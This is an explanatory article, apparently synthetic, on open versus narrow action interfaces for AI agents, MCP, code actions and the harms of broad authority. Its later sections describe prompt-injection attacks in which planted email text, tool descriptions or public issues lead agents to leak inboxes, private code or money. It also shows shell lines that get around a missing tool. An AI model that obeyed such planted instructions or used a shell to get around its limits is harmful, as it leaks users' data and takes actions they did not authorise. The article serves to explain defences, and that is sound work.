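# Open access to real-world tools or narrow action languages for AI agents

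## Agents, tools and action languages

An AI agent is a language model that works in a loop, choosing an action, reading the result and choosing again until the task is done. A language model on its own produces only text, so to change a file, book a flight or start a pump, it needs an interface that turns some of that text into real operations. Some developers make this interface very open, with a command line, a web browser and connections to live company data. Others offer a short list of commands for one machine or program, and their software rejects any other command.

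NIST, the US National Institute of Standards and Technology, writes that the usefulness of agents in the real world depends on how well they can interact with external systems and internal data, which favours open access. In favour of narrow action languages, Hong, She and colleagues (2026) argue in *Don't Make Models Guess Security and Safety* that a company with a lot to lose needs to know whether certain actions can be ruled out, even when someone is attacking the system, rather than how the agent usually behaves.

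### The agent loop

An agent consists of a model and the ordinary software around it, called the harness. *Agentic Large Language Models* (van Duijn, van der Meer and colleagues, 2026) writes this as "Agentic LLM = LLM + Harness", where LLM means large language model. The harness writes the prompts, processes the answers, calls outside programs and tracks the task's progress.

Anthropic's developer documentation *How tool use works* describes the loop step by step. The harness sends the model the user's request and a list of tools. A tool is an operation the model can request, such as a function, a service call or a shell command, and each has a schema that formally describes its arguments. The model replies either with ordinary text or with a structured request to use a tool. According to Anthropic's *Handle tool calls*, this request contains an identifier, the tool's name and an input that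 fits the schema. In Anthropic's words, "The model never runs anything on its own"; the harness reads the fields, runs the operation, adds the result to the conversation and sends the whole conversation back. The cycle repeats until the model replies without requesting a tool.

*Unrolling the Codex agent loop* (Bolin, 2026) describes how Codex CLI, OpenAI's coding agent, reads a file. The model calls a tool named `shell` with the command `cat README.md`, which prints the file's contents. The harness runs the command and appends the output to the prompt, so the model sees both its call and the output before it produces the next step. A single user request can lead to hundreds of these calls.

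A builder can therefore limit an agent at two points, parsing and execution. During parsing, the harness decides which text counts as an action. In *Learning CLI Agents with Structured Action Credit under Selective Observation* (2026), every reply must match one of two fixed patterns, one for code and one for a final answer. The system enforces the length limits in those patterns by constrained decoding, which blocks any token (a word or piece of a word) that could not lead to a valid reply at each step of generation. During execution, the harness or the operating system controls what an accepted action can reach.

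The same idea has a compact mathematical form. Arunkumar, Gangadharan and Buyya (2026), in *Agentic Artificial Intelligence (AI)*, write the agent's choice at step *t* as

Aₜ ~ π(Aₜ | Zₜ, Mₜ)

Here Aₜ is the action, Zₜ the reasoning the model has just produced, Mₜ its memory, and π the policy, which is the probability of the model picking each action. The action must come from the action space 𝒯, the set of actions that the agent can express and the harness will carry out. Training changes π, and good training makes a bad action rarer. Removing the action from 𝒯 makes its probability zero, even if the model is badly trained or misled.

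### From a menu to a screen

Action spaces range from narrow to open. In the narrowest, the agent picks one option from a short, fixed menu and supplies little or nothing else.

Typed functions come next. The agent fills in the arguments of named operations, usually as a JSON tool call, which is a structured record with one tool name and its arguments. *Communication Policy Evolution for Proactive LLM Agents* (2026) lists the 14 functions available to the airline agent in a widely used customer-service test, including `book_reservation`, `cancel_reservation`, `calculate` and `transfer_to_human_agents`. *Controlled Knowledge Engineering for Taxonomy Induction with Tool-Grounded LLM Agents* (2026) uses typed functions for an agent that builds classification schemes. The paper separates tools that only read from tools that change something, and each tool takes only the inputs it needs.

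A domain-specific language, such as the database query language SQL, goes a step further. It is a small formal language whose commands cover one kind of task, machine or program, and the agent can combine them as the grammar allows. General code, usually Python, is more open. A code action is a whole program, with variables and loops, that can call several tools before it returns anything. A shell is more open still because it can start any program installed on the machine.

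The number of commands in an interface is a poor guide to how open it is. *OS-Wizard* (2026) describes an agent that works through a single function, `computer_use`, with 14 actions for operating the screen and managing the task. The airline agent has the same number, but clicks and keystrokes can operate almost any program that has a window. The format is also a poor guide, because the `shell` tool in Codex is itself a typed function whose one required argument is a command to run. Adding a tool like that to a narrow interface as an escape hatch, for cases the other commands miss, makes the interface about as open as that tool.

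Arunkumar and colleagues compare the strengths and weaknesses of most of these designs. Predefined calls are safer because their scope is restricted, but schemas cause friction and the agent must manually carry state from one call to the next. Code allows rich control flow, but it can hit runtime errors and may escape its sandbox. Screen control works without the software maker's cooperation, but it is slow and brittle.

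### One cancellation, four ways

The airline test comes from *τ²-Bench* (2025). Its cancellation policy requires the agent to obtain the customer's identity, the reservation number and the reason for cancelling. If any part of the trip has already been flown, the agent cannot help and must transfer the customer to a human. Otherwise, it may cancel if the customer booked within the last 24 hours, the airline cancelled the flight, the ticket is business class, or the customer has insurance that covers the reason.

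Take a customer who booked reservation K4TZ9P (an invented number) five hours ago and has changed plans. With typed functions, the agent first calls `get_reservation_details`, reads the answer, and then emits something like this:

```json
{"name": "cancel_reservation", "input": {"reservation_id": "K4TZ9P"}}
```

This call does not include the 24-hour rule. According to the policy, the booking system does not check the cancellation rules, so the agent must. If the model misreads a date, the system will still process the cancellation. A builder could prevent this with a precondition check, which is ordinary code that blocks the call unless a stated condition holds.

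In a domain-specific language for bookings, the same step might read:

```
cancel K4TZ9P reason change_of_plan ground booked_within_24h
```

If the designers make the `ground` part compulsory and allow only the four grounds in the policy, a cancellation without a ground is a syntax error. The interpreter, the program that runs commands written in the language, can look up the booking time itself instead of relying on the model to supply it.

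In Python, one action can hold the look-up, the test and the cancellation:

```python
r = get_reservation_details("K4TZ9P")
if r.hours_since_booking <= 24 and not r.any_part_flown:
    cancel_reservation("K4TZ9P")
```

The same program would process fifty bookings if it were put in a loop. But the test on its second line is there only because the model wrote it.

A shell that holds the password to the airline's database needs no cancellation function at all:

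```
psql bookings -c "UPDATE reservations SET status='cancelled' WHERE id='K4TZ9P'"
```

This command changes the booking record directly and skips the refund. Without the `WHERE` clause, it cancels every booking in the table. With the same shell, an agent could also copy out the passenger list.

### Expressive power and authority

If the Python program can reach only those two functions, the Python and typed-function versions can do the same things to the airline. They differ in expressive power, meaning which sequences, loops and combinations of actions the agent can state in the language. The shell also differs in authority, meaning the data an action can reach and the effects it can have, regardless of the language it is written in. Arguments about open and narrow agents often treat expressive power and authority as one property, because the usual comparison is between a small toy language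 and a fully connected shell. Small languages with broad authority and expressive languages with little authority also exist.

| | Little authority | Much authority |
|---|---|---|
| **Low expressive power** | A lamp-control language: `on`, `off`, `dim 40` | A language of five commands, one of which is `transfer <amount> to <account>` |
| **High expressive power** | Python with no network and no files | A shell holding live credentials |

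The money-transfer language is tiny, but one wrong command in it can empty an account, while the closed-off Python can express any computation but do little with the result except return it. The agents in *Learning CLI Agents with Structured Action Credit under Selective Observation* are much like the Python case, since they write real shell commands that run in a sandbox isolated from the network and the rest of the file system.

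The two variables are not fully independent. An agent limited to single calls can still make fifty bookings by repeating the agent loop, but it needs fifty calls, and the model must make a new decision before each one. So some of the benefit of a richer language is speed and lower cost, and how much it adds beyond that has to be measured. Authority accumulates across all of an agent's tools. Bolin notes that the Codex sandbox covers only Codex's own shell tool. Tools from outside servers, which connect through the Model Context Protocol (an open standard for offering tools to agents), have to enforce their own limits. An agent with a tightly confined shell therefore still has a lot of authority if it also has an unconfined payments tool.

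Least privilege is an old rule in security engineering that a program should get only the authority its task needs. It goes back to Saltzer and Schroeder's *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems*, and it doesn't limit how rich the program's language may be. Prompt injection is a further reason to apply the rule to agents. In such an attack, someone plants text in a web page, document or tool result, and the agent treats it as an instruction. An attacker who can steer the agent this way gains whatever authority it has, even if the user is well-meaning and the model is competent. A US government request for information in the Federal Register (2026) lists least privilege among the measures that organisations have begun to apply to agents.

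### Sorting tools and agents

In January 2025 NIST held a workshop with about 140 experts on how to classify the tools agents use, and NIST's *Lessons Learned from the Consortium*, published that August, offers two schemes. The first sorts tools by purpose. Perception tools bring in information, for example from an internal database, an internet search or a view of the screen. Reasoning tools, such as calculators, simulations and memory, help the model think beyond its own output. Action tools affect the environment directly, which NIST says includes running code, logging in, operating a browser, moving a robotic arm and making phone calls. The distinction is useful because "open access" tends to bundle reading with acting, and a builder can separate them, for example by letting an agent search the whole internet without letting it change anything.

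The second scheme crosses what a tool may change with how far the builder can trust the surroundings.

| | Read only | Constrained write | Write |
|---|---|---|---|
| **Trusted environment** | Answering from a document store | Use of one application's interface | Coding agent in a trusted repository |
| **Untrusted environment** | Research on the open web | Browser use | Control of a whole computer |

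Both of these dimensions concern authority and exposure to attack, not expressive power. NIST observes that builders limit write access either by providing tools with restricted interactions or by constraining a tool that would otherwise be almost unlimited, such as code execution. The first method usually reduces expressive power along with authority, while the second can limit authority without making the language less expressive.

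Hong and colleagues sort whole agents by the scope of their tasks. A general-purpose agent serves an open-ended set of tasks with broadly applicable tools. Their examples include ChatGPT's agent mode and command-line agents such as Claude Code, which can edit files, run commands and use the internet. A domain-specific agent has a fixed scope and only the tools relevant to it, like the airline agent, which is not allowed to go online or run arbitrary code. A builder who knows all the tasks and tools in advance can write the agent's rules precisely enough to check, which is hard to do for an agent that might do anything. The definition removes internet access (authority) and arbitrary code (expressive power) together, and it leaves open whether a domain-specific agent has to give up both.

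### Two questions to test

The question "Do useful agents need open access?" is too vague to test. It combines two questions that need different kinds of evidence.

The first question is which tasks fail when a builder narrows the interface. An experiment can answer it by keeping the model and tasks the same, changing the interface, and comparing task success, the share of tasks completed correctly. A fair experiment changes only one variable at a time. Moving from a shell to typed functions reduces both expressive power and authority, so if success falls, it is unclear which reduction was responsible. Some tasks fail because no sequence of permitted actions reaches the goal, and only a change to the interface will help. Others fail because the model misses a sequence that would work, which a better model or clearer documentation might fix.

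The second question is which harms become impossible. A harm is impossible when no sequence of actions that the harness accepts can produce it, whatever text the model emits. To establish that, someone has to examine the harness and its rules, since a thousand runs without an accident show only that the accident is uncommon. The guarantee depends on the harness code being correct, and it covers only the harms that the rules exclude. Hong and colleagues give the example of a check that the person asking for a cancellation owns the ticket. With that check in place, and no other route to the booking records, the agent cannot cancel a stranger's flight, but it can still cancel the wrong one of the customer's own flights.

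## How an agent is connected to real tools and data

Developers give agents open access in four main ways: JSON tool calls, Model Context Protocol (MCP) servers, programs or shell commands that the model writes, and control of a screen. These differ in what enters the model's context (all the text and images it reads before choosing an action), what the model outputs, what software carries out the action, and whose credentials that software uses. The credentials largely determine what the agent can do, because an outside service checks the account behind a request and usually cannot detect whether a person or a model decided to send it.

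| Connection | What enters the context | What the model emits | What executes | Whose credentials |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| JSON tool call | Tool definitions, then every result | A tool name and arguments | A function in the harness | The account the developer gave the function |
| MCP server | Definitions from the server's author, then every result | A tool name and arguments | The server, local or remote | A user's grant, or keys stored on the machine |
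| Code or shell | Whatever the program prints | A program or command | An interpreter or shell | The account that runs it, plus any keys it can read |
| Screen control | Screenshots | Clicks and keystrokes | The programs on the screen | The accounts logged in on that machine |

### JSON tool calls

In the simplest arrangement, the developer builds the tools into the harness. Suppose a company wants an agent to work with its customer support tickets. The developer writes a function, `get_ticket`, that fetches one ticket from the company's database, and a short definition of the function. To request ticket 17, the model outputs `{"name": "get_ticket", "input": {"id": 17}}`.

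The function logs in with a key the developer stored in the harness. The model never reads the key, but it can still use whatever access the key gives. If that includes every ticket, the agent can read them all, even ones the person making the request has no right to see. A careful developer makes the function check that person's permissions first.

The main drawback is the amount of work, because someone has to connect each service to each agent separately. For example, an agent from another company can't use `get_ticket` until someone adapts the tool to that agent's harness.

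### The Model Context Protocol

Anthropic launched MCP in November 2024 to replace these custom integrations with one standard (Anthropic, *Code execution with MCP*, November 2025). The owner of a service writes an MCP server, a program that offers tools. Any agent whose harness contains an MCP client can then use its tools.

In December 2025 Anthropic donated the protocol to the Agentic AI Foundation, a new fund under the Linux Foundation, which hosts open-source projects. The Agentic AI Foundation's announcement (2025) lists Anthropic, OpenAI and the payments company Block as founding contributors.

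At the time of the donation, Model Context Protocol's *MCP joins Agentic AI Foundation* (2025) reported 10,000 active servers, support in products including ChatGPT, Claude, Gemini and Microsoft Copilot, and over 97 million monthly downloads of the kits that developers use to build clients and servers. By July 2026, monthly downloads were close to half a billion, according to Model Context Protocol's release announcement (2026). The two figures are not quite comparable because the earlier one covers only the Python and TypeScript kits, as Anthropic's *Donating the Model Context Protocol and establishing of the Agentic AI Foundation* specifies, while the later one covers four languages. Downloads are also a loose measure of use, since automated builds fetch the same kit repeatedly. The July announcement includes one figure closer to actual use, reporting that agents now make nearly 20% of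 monthly interactive queries at Honeycomb, a software monitoring company.

### One MCP call, message by message

The current revision of the protocol is dated July 28, 2026, and Model Context Protocol's *A More Predictable Release Cycle for MCP* (2026) sets March 30, 2027 as the target for the next. Earlier revisions opened a session with a handshake, and the client then attached a session number to each request. The July revision dropped both. Developers now use "session" to mean a series of independent requests, each of which carries the protocol version and the client's details.

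The client begins by sending `tools/list`. In the format that Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026) defines, a ticket server's reply would include an entry like this:

```json
{
  "name": "get_ticket",
  "description": "Return one support ticket by its number",
  "inputSchema": {
    "type": "object",
    "properties": {"id": {"type": "integer"}},
    "required": ["id"]
  }
}
```

Next, the harness copies the definitions into the model's context. The model picks tools by their descriptions, so text by the server's author, who may be a stranger, now sits in the prompt (and an attacker can hide instructions there). When the model emits a tool call, the client forwards it to the server:

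```json
{"jsonrpc": "2.0", "id": 2, "method": "tools/call",
 "params": {"name": "get_ticket", "arguments": {"id": 17}}}
```

The server runs its own code, fetches the ticket and returns it with a flag showing whether the call failed. The client adds the result to the conversation. An error message can help the model correct its request and try again. In one of the specification's examples, the server rejects a departure date in the past and includes today's date in the error message.

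Without sessions, the model has to carry information from one call to the next. A shopping server, for example, returns a basket number when it creates a basket, and the model repeats that number whenever it adds an item. The specification advises servers that identify their callers to check the caller's permission on every call, so that knowing a basket number isn't enough to change the basket.

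### Why the client receives every tool

A `tools/list` request contains a page marker and details about the client, but nothing about the user's task, so the server has no basis for choosing the relevant tools. The specification also forbids servers from varying the list between connections or in response to earlier requests. The list may still change over time or depend on the caller's authorization, so a caller with read-only permission might receive only the reading tools. Clients can store a stable list, and model providers can reuse their processing of that part of the prompt.

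Tool definitions take up space in the model's context. According to Anthropic, most clients load all the definitions at the start, and an agent with thousands of tools may process hundreds of thousands of tokens before it reaches the user's request. The protocol leaves the presentation of tools to the client, which can instead filter the list or give the model a search tool that returns definitions on demand. Hiding a definition saves tokens, but it reduces the agent's authority only if the client also refuses calls to the hidden tool.

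### Consent and credentials

The Model Context Protocol specification recommends that a person always be able to deny a tool call, and that clients show users a tool's inputs before sending them. Both are "should" rules, which in technical standards are weaker than "must". The protocol's overview is stricter, and lists as a key principle that users "must explicitly consent to and understand all data access and operations". In practice, the client has to implement this. An ordinary `tools/call` message has no field for the user's approval, so a server can't distinguish a call that someone read and approved from one that the client approved automatically.

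A server can, however, respond to a call by requesting more input instead of returning a result. The client then repeats the call with the answer attached. The database company Supabase plans to use this to request confirmation before running queries that would delete data.

Authorization is optional under Model Context Protocol's *Authorization* (2026). Remote servers that support it should use OAuth 2.1, a version of the system behind the familiar "allow this app to access your files" screens. The process works as follows:

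1. The client sends a request, and the server refuses it and can name the permission needed, for example `files:read`.
2. The user logs in through a browser and approves the access.
3. The client receives an access token (a secret string, unrelated to the tokens of text that a model reads) and attaches it to every later request.

Each access token works for only one server, and a server must not accept or pass on any token that wasn't issued for it. Clients should request only the permissions they need (the principle of least privilege). If the agent later tries to write a file, the server can refuse and name `files:write` as the missing permission. The client then requests a new token that covers both the old and new permissions. An agent's authority can therefore grow during a long task unless someone reduces it.

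Servers that run on the user's own machine instead take their credentials from the environment, meaning keys and settings already present on the computer. If the user starts a local ticket server with an administrator's key, the server has an administrator's authority, even if the user only wanted the agent to read a few tickets.

### Code actions and shells

When an agent acts by writing code, an interpreter runs the program, and the printed output or error message goes back into the model's context. In *Executable Code Actions Elicit Better LLM Agents*, Wang, Chen and colleagues (2024) proposed using Python for all of an agent's actions. Python gives the agent loops and variables, and lets it use existing packages instead of tools that someone has to build by hand. In their tests, code matched or beat JSON and plain text for most models.

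A shell works the same way, and many of the programs it can start print their own instructions on request, so the instructions take up no context until then. In *Code execution with MCP*, a comment on Anthropic's post of the same name, Willison (2025) reports that he has stopped using MCP with coding agents because command-line programs and software libraries achieve the same goals more effectively. That is one developer's experience with coding, where good command-line programs already exist for most jobs.

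Code can also call MCP tools. In a design that Anthropic describes, the harness presents each tool as a file, in a folder named after its server. The model lists the folders, reads the few files it needs, and writes a program that calls those tools. The harness can also keep private data out of the model's context. For example, it can replace customers' email addresses with placeholders, then restore the real addresses when the program sends the data to another service.

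### Fifty records, two ways

Suppose an agent has to read 50 support tickets of about 1,000 tokens each (invented figures) and save a summary that counts the open tickets and lists those open for more than two weeks.

With one JSON call per turn, the model calls `get_ticket` 50 times, calls `save_summary` once and then tells the user that it has finished. This takes 52 model turns, and all 50,000 tokens of ticket text enter the context. The harness also resends the whole conversation on every turn, so the model processes the early tickets again and again. For *n* tickets of *r* tokens each, the total ticket text processed is

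r × (n(n + 1)/2 + n)

The fraction adds up the number of tickets in the context on each turn (0, 1, 2, … *n*), through the turn that saves the summary, and the extra *n* is for the closing reply. Here the total is 1,325,000 tokens. Providers often charge less for text they have recently processed, so the bill rises more slowly than the token count. Some harnesses also accept many calls in one reply. If the agent fetches all 50 tickets in one turn, the job takes three turns and the total falls to 100,000 tokens, although every ticket still enters the context.

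As a code action, the same job looks like this:

```python
tickets = [get_ticket(i) for i in range(1, 51)]
still_open = [t for t in tickets if t["status"] == "open"]
late = [t["id"] for t in still_open if t["days_open"] > 14]
save_summary(f"{len(still_open)} open; over two weeks: {late}")
print("Summary saved for", len(tickets), "tickets")
```

This takes two model turns, one to write the script and one to report back. None of the ticket text enters the context, and Python does the counting.

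However, the model wrote the script without seeing any tickets. If some are marked `reopened`, the script leaves them out, and its printed line doesn't show the mistake. The saving also depends on the kind of summary. To summarise what customers are complaining about, the model has to read their complaints. A script could cut each ticket down to the complaint, but that text would still have to enter the context.

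Anthropic gives the example of an agent that copies a meeting transcript from Google Drive into a customer record in Salesforce. If the agent calls the tools directly, the transcript passes through the model twice, once as the result of the first call and once as an argument of the second. For a two-hour meeting, that could add 50,000 tokens. If the agent writes code instead, the transcript can go straight from one service to the other. Anthropic says total token use falls from 150,000 to 2,000, or by 98.7%, when the agent reads only the tool definitions it needs.

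This example suits code very well, since the task needs only two tools and the model has no reason to read the transcript. An agent with five tools and short results would save far less. Anthropic calls the 98.7% a saving in time and cost, but the figure measures only the fall in tokens. Time and cost also depend on the services and on where the code runs. Anthropic acknowledges in the post that model-written code needs a secure sandbox, resource limits and monitoring, which direct calls avoid. The Model Context Protocol blog describes an experimental extension that would solve part of the problem without code, by letting clients send files directly to storage while the model handles only details such as the file's name and size.

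### What a shell does to finer tools

Suppose a developer wants an agent to read files but not change them, and so leaves out the `write_file` tool. If the agent has a shell that can write to the folder, it can still run this:

```
echo "new contents" > report.txt
```

Blocking `echo` would do little to stop an agent from writing files, because `cp`, `tee`, `sed -i` and a one-line Python script can all write them. An agent with a shell but no tool for fetching web pages can run `curl`, a standard program for network requests. Leaving out a tool limits an agent only if none of its other tools can do the same job, and an unconfined shell can do almost anything that a file or network tool can.

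An agent with a shell can also get around the limits of an MCP server. Suppose a local ticket server offers only `get_ticket`, but the key it uses also allows deletion. If the shell runs under the same user account as the server, the agent can often read that key from the environment or a settings file. It could then contact the ticket service directly and delete tickets.

The developer therefore has to set the limit in the operating system. If the shell runs under an account without write permission, or in a sandbox where the folder is read-only, `echo`, `sed` and Python all fail to write to the folder. A `write_file` tool is still useful beside a shell that is allowed to write, because the harness can show the user the exact change before making it, which is much harder with an arbitrary command. But this protects the user only when the model uses that tool, and the model can always use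 the shell instead.

### Screen control

For screen control, the harness takes a screenshot and adds it to the context. The model emits an action, such as a click 412 pixels across and 300 down. The harness passes the click to the operating system as if it came from a mouse, then takes another screenshot. The program that receives the click acts through whatever accounts are already logged in. To cancel a flight, the agent would open the airline's website, find the booking and press the cancel button, and the website would treat this as the customer's own request. Any checks and confirmation pages meant for people would also apply to the agent.

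Nobody has to write a connector for this, but it makes fine-grained permissions difficult. The coordinates of a click don't show whether the button there opens a message or deletes an account, so a harness meant to block deletions has to work out what is on the screen. As with a shell, an agent can also use logged-in accounts to do things it has no tool for. For example, an agent with no email tool can send email from a browser logged in to the user's mailbox. A developer can limit this by giving the agent a separate machine logged in only to the accounts it needs.

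### The case for openness

Supporters' first argument for open connections is that they save developers work. If each of ten agents needs a custom link to each of a hundred services, developers have to build 1,000 integrations. With a shared protocol, they need only ten clients and a hundred servers, or 110 pieces of software. Anthropic makes this argument for MCP.

Supporters also point to the limits of a model without tools. In *MCP 2026 changes the rules*, Granados (2026) describes a model that can only suggest steps, so the user has to open the calendar, find the document and send the email. Because the model doesn't see the results, it guesses at what it is missing, and a wrong guess can waste hours.

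Wang and colleagues object that developers usually design predefined tools for specific tasks, while an agent with Python can load an existing package for a task its developer never considered. Anthropic adds that such an agent can save working code as a function and reuse it later, so it gains new operations as it works.

Saving integration work is a reason to use a shared protocol, but it doesn't require giving an agent broad authority. A company could publish an MCP server whose only tool is `get_ticket`. Granados compares an agent that has tools with a model that has none, but an agent with only five narrow commands would also spare the user much of the manual work. Unforeseen tasks are a stronger argument against narrow interfaces, because developers can't write commands for tasks they haven't thought of. However, many of these tasks are new combinations of familiar operations, such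 as an unusual report based on tickets the agent can already read. Those combinations need a more expressive language, but an agent needs more authority only for tasks that involve new data or new kinds of effects.

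## How open access leads to harm

Broad authority can lead to harm in three ways. Someone can plant text that the agent obeys, the agent can make a mistake, or the model can decide on its own to do something nobody authorised. Builders have to consider each separately, because a filter that catches planted text won't stop an accidental deletion.

### From an email to a data leak

Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) describes an imaginary assistant called Email-Bot, which summarises a user's new mail, keeps track of older messages and sends replies. An attacker sends the user a spam email containing an instruction for Email-Bot to forward the private contents of the inbox to the attacker.

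Later, the user asks for a summary of the new mail. The harness fetches the messages and adds them to the context, which now contains both the attacker's instruction and the user's request. Willison (2025) explains in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* that everything the model receives becomes one sequence of tokens, and that models can't reliably judge an instruction by where it came from. If the model obeys the email, it calls one tool to fetch the older messages and then another to send an email to the attacker's address. Both calls are well-formed and use tools the agent needs for its normal work, so the harness runs them with the user's account.

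The attack doesn't work every time, because a model's output varies from run to run. A warning in the prompt can make it fail more often, but the attacker can keep rephrasing the instruction.

Willison coined the term "prompt injection" after SQL injection, an older attack on websites that mix a visitor's text into database commands. He distinguishes it from jailbreaking, where someone tricks a model into saying something it shouldn't. With prompt injection, the user is often the victim.

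The email attack needs only a few ordinary tool calls and no code or shell. A less expressive action language wouldn't prevent it if the agent could still read the inbox and email strangers.

### Private data, untrusted content and a way out

The theft requires three conditions, which Willison calls the "lethal trifecta": access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to send data out. If any one is missing, the attacker can't steal the data, even if the model obeys the attacker's instructions.

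Meta's Rule of Two turns this into a design rule. Until models can reliably detect and refuse prompt injection, an agent should have at most two of these properties in one session:

- **A:** it processes untrustworthy input.
- **B:** it can reach sensitive systems or private data.
- **C:** it can change something or communicate externally.

Property C is wider than Willison's third condition because it also covers actions such as deleting a file or paying a deposit. If a task needs all three properties in a single session, Meta requires supervision by a person or some other reliable check.

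Email-Bot could satisfy the rule by reading mail only from trusted senders, which removes A. It could run in a test environment with no real mail, which removes B but makes it much less useful as an email assistant. It could also restrict C by sending mail only to trusted recipients or only after the user approves the draft. An agent can also change its combination of A, B and C partway through a session. For example, it could research a question on the web, then permanently lose the ability to communicate externally before it opens internal files.

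Human approval may be the weakest of these controls. Willison quotes an Anthropic study of 1,053 paid testers in which one permission request per session was for a clearly dangerous command. Only 13.6% of the testers refused it. Anthropic says that auto mode, in which software approves its coding agent's actions, would have blocked 89% of the dangerous commands. Anthropic sells auto mode, but the testers' low refusal rate fits Meta's warning about users who confirm without reading.

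Preventing data leaks also takes more than removing an agent's email tool. According to Willison, an agent can leak data through any web request, including one that loads an image, or through a link that the user clicks. Anthropic's Claude Cowork could contact only a short list of domains by default, but the list included Anthropic's file service. In January 2026, the security firm Prompt Armor showed that an attacker with an account on that service could receive a victim's files.

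ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode, which OpenAI began rolling out widely in June 2026, uses fixed rules to limit outbound requests. Planted text can still reach the model and distort its answer, but there are fewer ways for it to get data out. OpenAI's security chief says the mode removes some functionality and is for people at elevated risk. Willison infers that ChatGPT's default settings don't provide robust protection against a determined attacker.

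### The confused deputy

In computer security, a confused deputy is a program that someone tricks into using its authority on their behalf. Email-Bot is a confused deputy because an attacker who can't access the user's mailbox can send mail to Email-Bot, which has that access.

The same thing can happen with the ticket tools from the previous section. Suppose a support agent has two functions, `get_ticket` and `reply_to_customer`, and its key covers every ticket. A customer can't see other people's tickets, but can submit one asking the agent to include the last ten complaints in its reply. If the agent complies, the database returns the complaints because the agent's key is valid.

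Willison describes a real case in which GitHub's MCP server let an agent read public issues, read private code and publish proposed changes. A stranger could write an instruction in a public issue, and an agent that obeyed it would copy private code into a public proposal. OpenAI's *Agent security in the enterprise* (2026) makes the general point that a valid credential may give access to a system without establishing which actions its holder is authorised to take.

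In the support example, if `get_ticket` checked the customer's own permissions, the agent would have nothing to leak even if it obeyed the planted instruction.

### Poisoned tool descriptions

An attacker who controls an MCP server can also plant text in a tool's description, and so influence the agent without sending the user anything. For example, a weather tool's description might contain an instruction for the model to include the user's recent notes in every weather request.

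Text in one tool's description can also affect how the agent uses other tools, because all the descriptions share one context. Jing, Hu and colleagues (2026) write in *Isolation as a First-Class Principle for LLM-Agent System Safety* that metadata can change which tool an agent prefers before any tool has returned a result. They also point out that a sequence of calls can do damage even if each call looks harmless, so checking calls one at a time can miss the attack.

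Reviewing a server only at installation isn't enough, because its tool list may change later. A developer can prevent such changes by writing all the tool definitions and fixing them in the harness. This works even if the tools are powerful, but the agent is still exposed to whatever text they return.

### How AgentDojo tests injection

Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues (2024), in *AgentDojo*, built a widely used test of prompt injection. It simulates an office suite, the messaging service Slack, a travel agency and a bank. At launch it had 97 user tasks, 27 attacker goals and 74 tools, going by the counts for each environment (a caption in the paper gives 70 tools). Each security case pairs a user task with an attacker goal from the same environment, for a total of

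40 × 6 + 21 × 5 + 20 × 7 + 16 × 9 = 629

In one banking case, the user asks the agent to pay a bill stored in a file. The researchers plant text in the data the agent will read, telling it to send as much money as possible to the attacker. Afterwards, ordinary code checks the agent's output and the bank's records to see whether the agent paid the bill and whether it sent the attacker money. The researchers didn't use a language model as the judge because the planted text might fool it too.

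The test produces three scores:

- the share of user tasks the agent completes without an attack
- the share of attacked cases in which it completes the user's task without harmful side effects
- the share of attacked cases in which the attacker's goal is met

In 2024, GPT-4o carried out the attacker's task in 47.7% of cases when the planted text correctly named both the model and the user. When either name was wrong, the rate fell to about 23%. In the Slack environment, where the attacker controls much of what the tools return, attacks succeeded 92% of the time. More capable models tended to be easier to attack, possibly because weaker ones often failed at the attacker's task even when they attempted it.

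In 17% of the paper's cases, the tools that the user's task needs are also enough for the attack. In the other 83%, the attack needs an additional tool, often one that sends or changes data when the user only wants to read it. An interface that offered only the tools each task needs would block all of those attacks. But a builder can't always choose the tools in advance, because the result of one call may determine what the agent has to do next.

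### Flaws in the tests

Bhagwatkar, Kasa and colleagues (2025), in *Indirect Prompt Injections*, found that in some AgentDojo cases the attack overwrites information the agent needs. It may replace the amounts on a bill, for instance, so the agent can't pay the bill correctly even if it ignores the attack. They also found that some scoring code was too strict. In one task, the agent has to send someone a summary, and the code checks that the person's inbox contains exactly one more message than before, so an agent that sends the right summary and a second message fails. After they corrected these faults, GPT-4o's task success under attack rose from 60.9% to 72.2%.

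They found a larger error in another test, Agent Security Bench. Its software added the attacker's tools to the agent's selection even when the agent hadn't chosen them, then counted any use of those tools as a successful attack. Once the agent could choose its own tools, the attack success rate dropped from 73.6% to 9.25%.

These errors made agents look worse than they were, but testing only against a fixed set of weak attacks can overstate how well a defence works. Bhagwatkar and colleagues tested their own filter, which removes suspicious instructions from tool results, on AgentDojo's Slack cases. It stopped every standard attack. They then tried planted text disguised as trusted metadata, followed by attacks that a language model revised over ten rounds using feedback on its failures. By the end, 30% of the attacks had succeeded.

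### Current models

In a test that Anthropic commissioned from Trajectory Labs in July 2026, none of 720 injection attempts succeeded against Claude Fable 5, Opus 5 or Sonnet 5 in auto mode. This looks far better than the 47.7% attack success rate against GPT-4o on AgentDojo, but the attacks and the agents' tasks were different. Auto mode also adds its own check on the agent's actions, so the result doesn't measure only the models' resistance to injection.

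Zero successes don't prove that the true rate is zero. The 720 attempts came from 72 scenarios. If those scenarios were independent and typical of real attacks, a true success rate of about 4% would still produce no successes in roughly one test out of twenty, since (1 − 0.04)⁷² ≈ 0.05. Treating all 720 attempts as independent lowers that figure to about 0.4%. Attackers can also keep trying. If each attempt succeeds with probability *p*, the chance of at least one success in *n* independent attempts is

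1 − (1 − p)ⁿ

With *p* at 0.4% and 1,000 attempts, this comes to about 98%.

Willison, who reported the test in August, would like more independent confirmation. He describes a software project whose instructions tell the agent to run a helper package before the tests. The request looks routine, but the package steals the agent's data. He doesn't see how any version of auto mode could prevent this, and he now wants to find a practical way to run agents without access to data or tools that could cause harm.

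### Honest mistakes

In July 2025 a coding agent from the software company Replit deleted the live database of Jason Lemkin, an investor who was trying out the agent, although he had told it to make no changes. Nobody had attacked the agent. It had permission to alter the live database, so no safeguard outside the model blocked the deletion.

Replit's chief executive, Amjad Masad, apologised and said that the company would separate development databases from live ones, which would have prevented this loss. The agent could still have used all of SQL on a development copy, so the fix reduces its authority without restricting its language. Willison similarly recommends that any keys coding agents can see belong to accounts outside the live system and have strict spending caps.

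The Rule of Two wouldn't necessarily help here. It allows an agent that reads only trusted instructions to have both private data and the power to change it. Meta lists agent mistakes and excessive privileges among the problems its rule doesn't cover, and presents the rule as a supplement to least privilege.

### Rules kept in text and broken with tools

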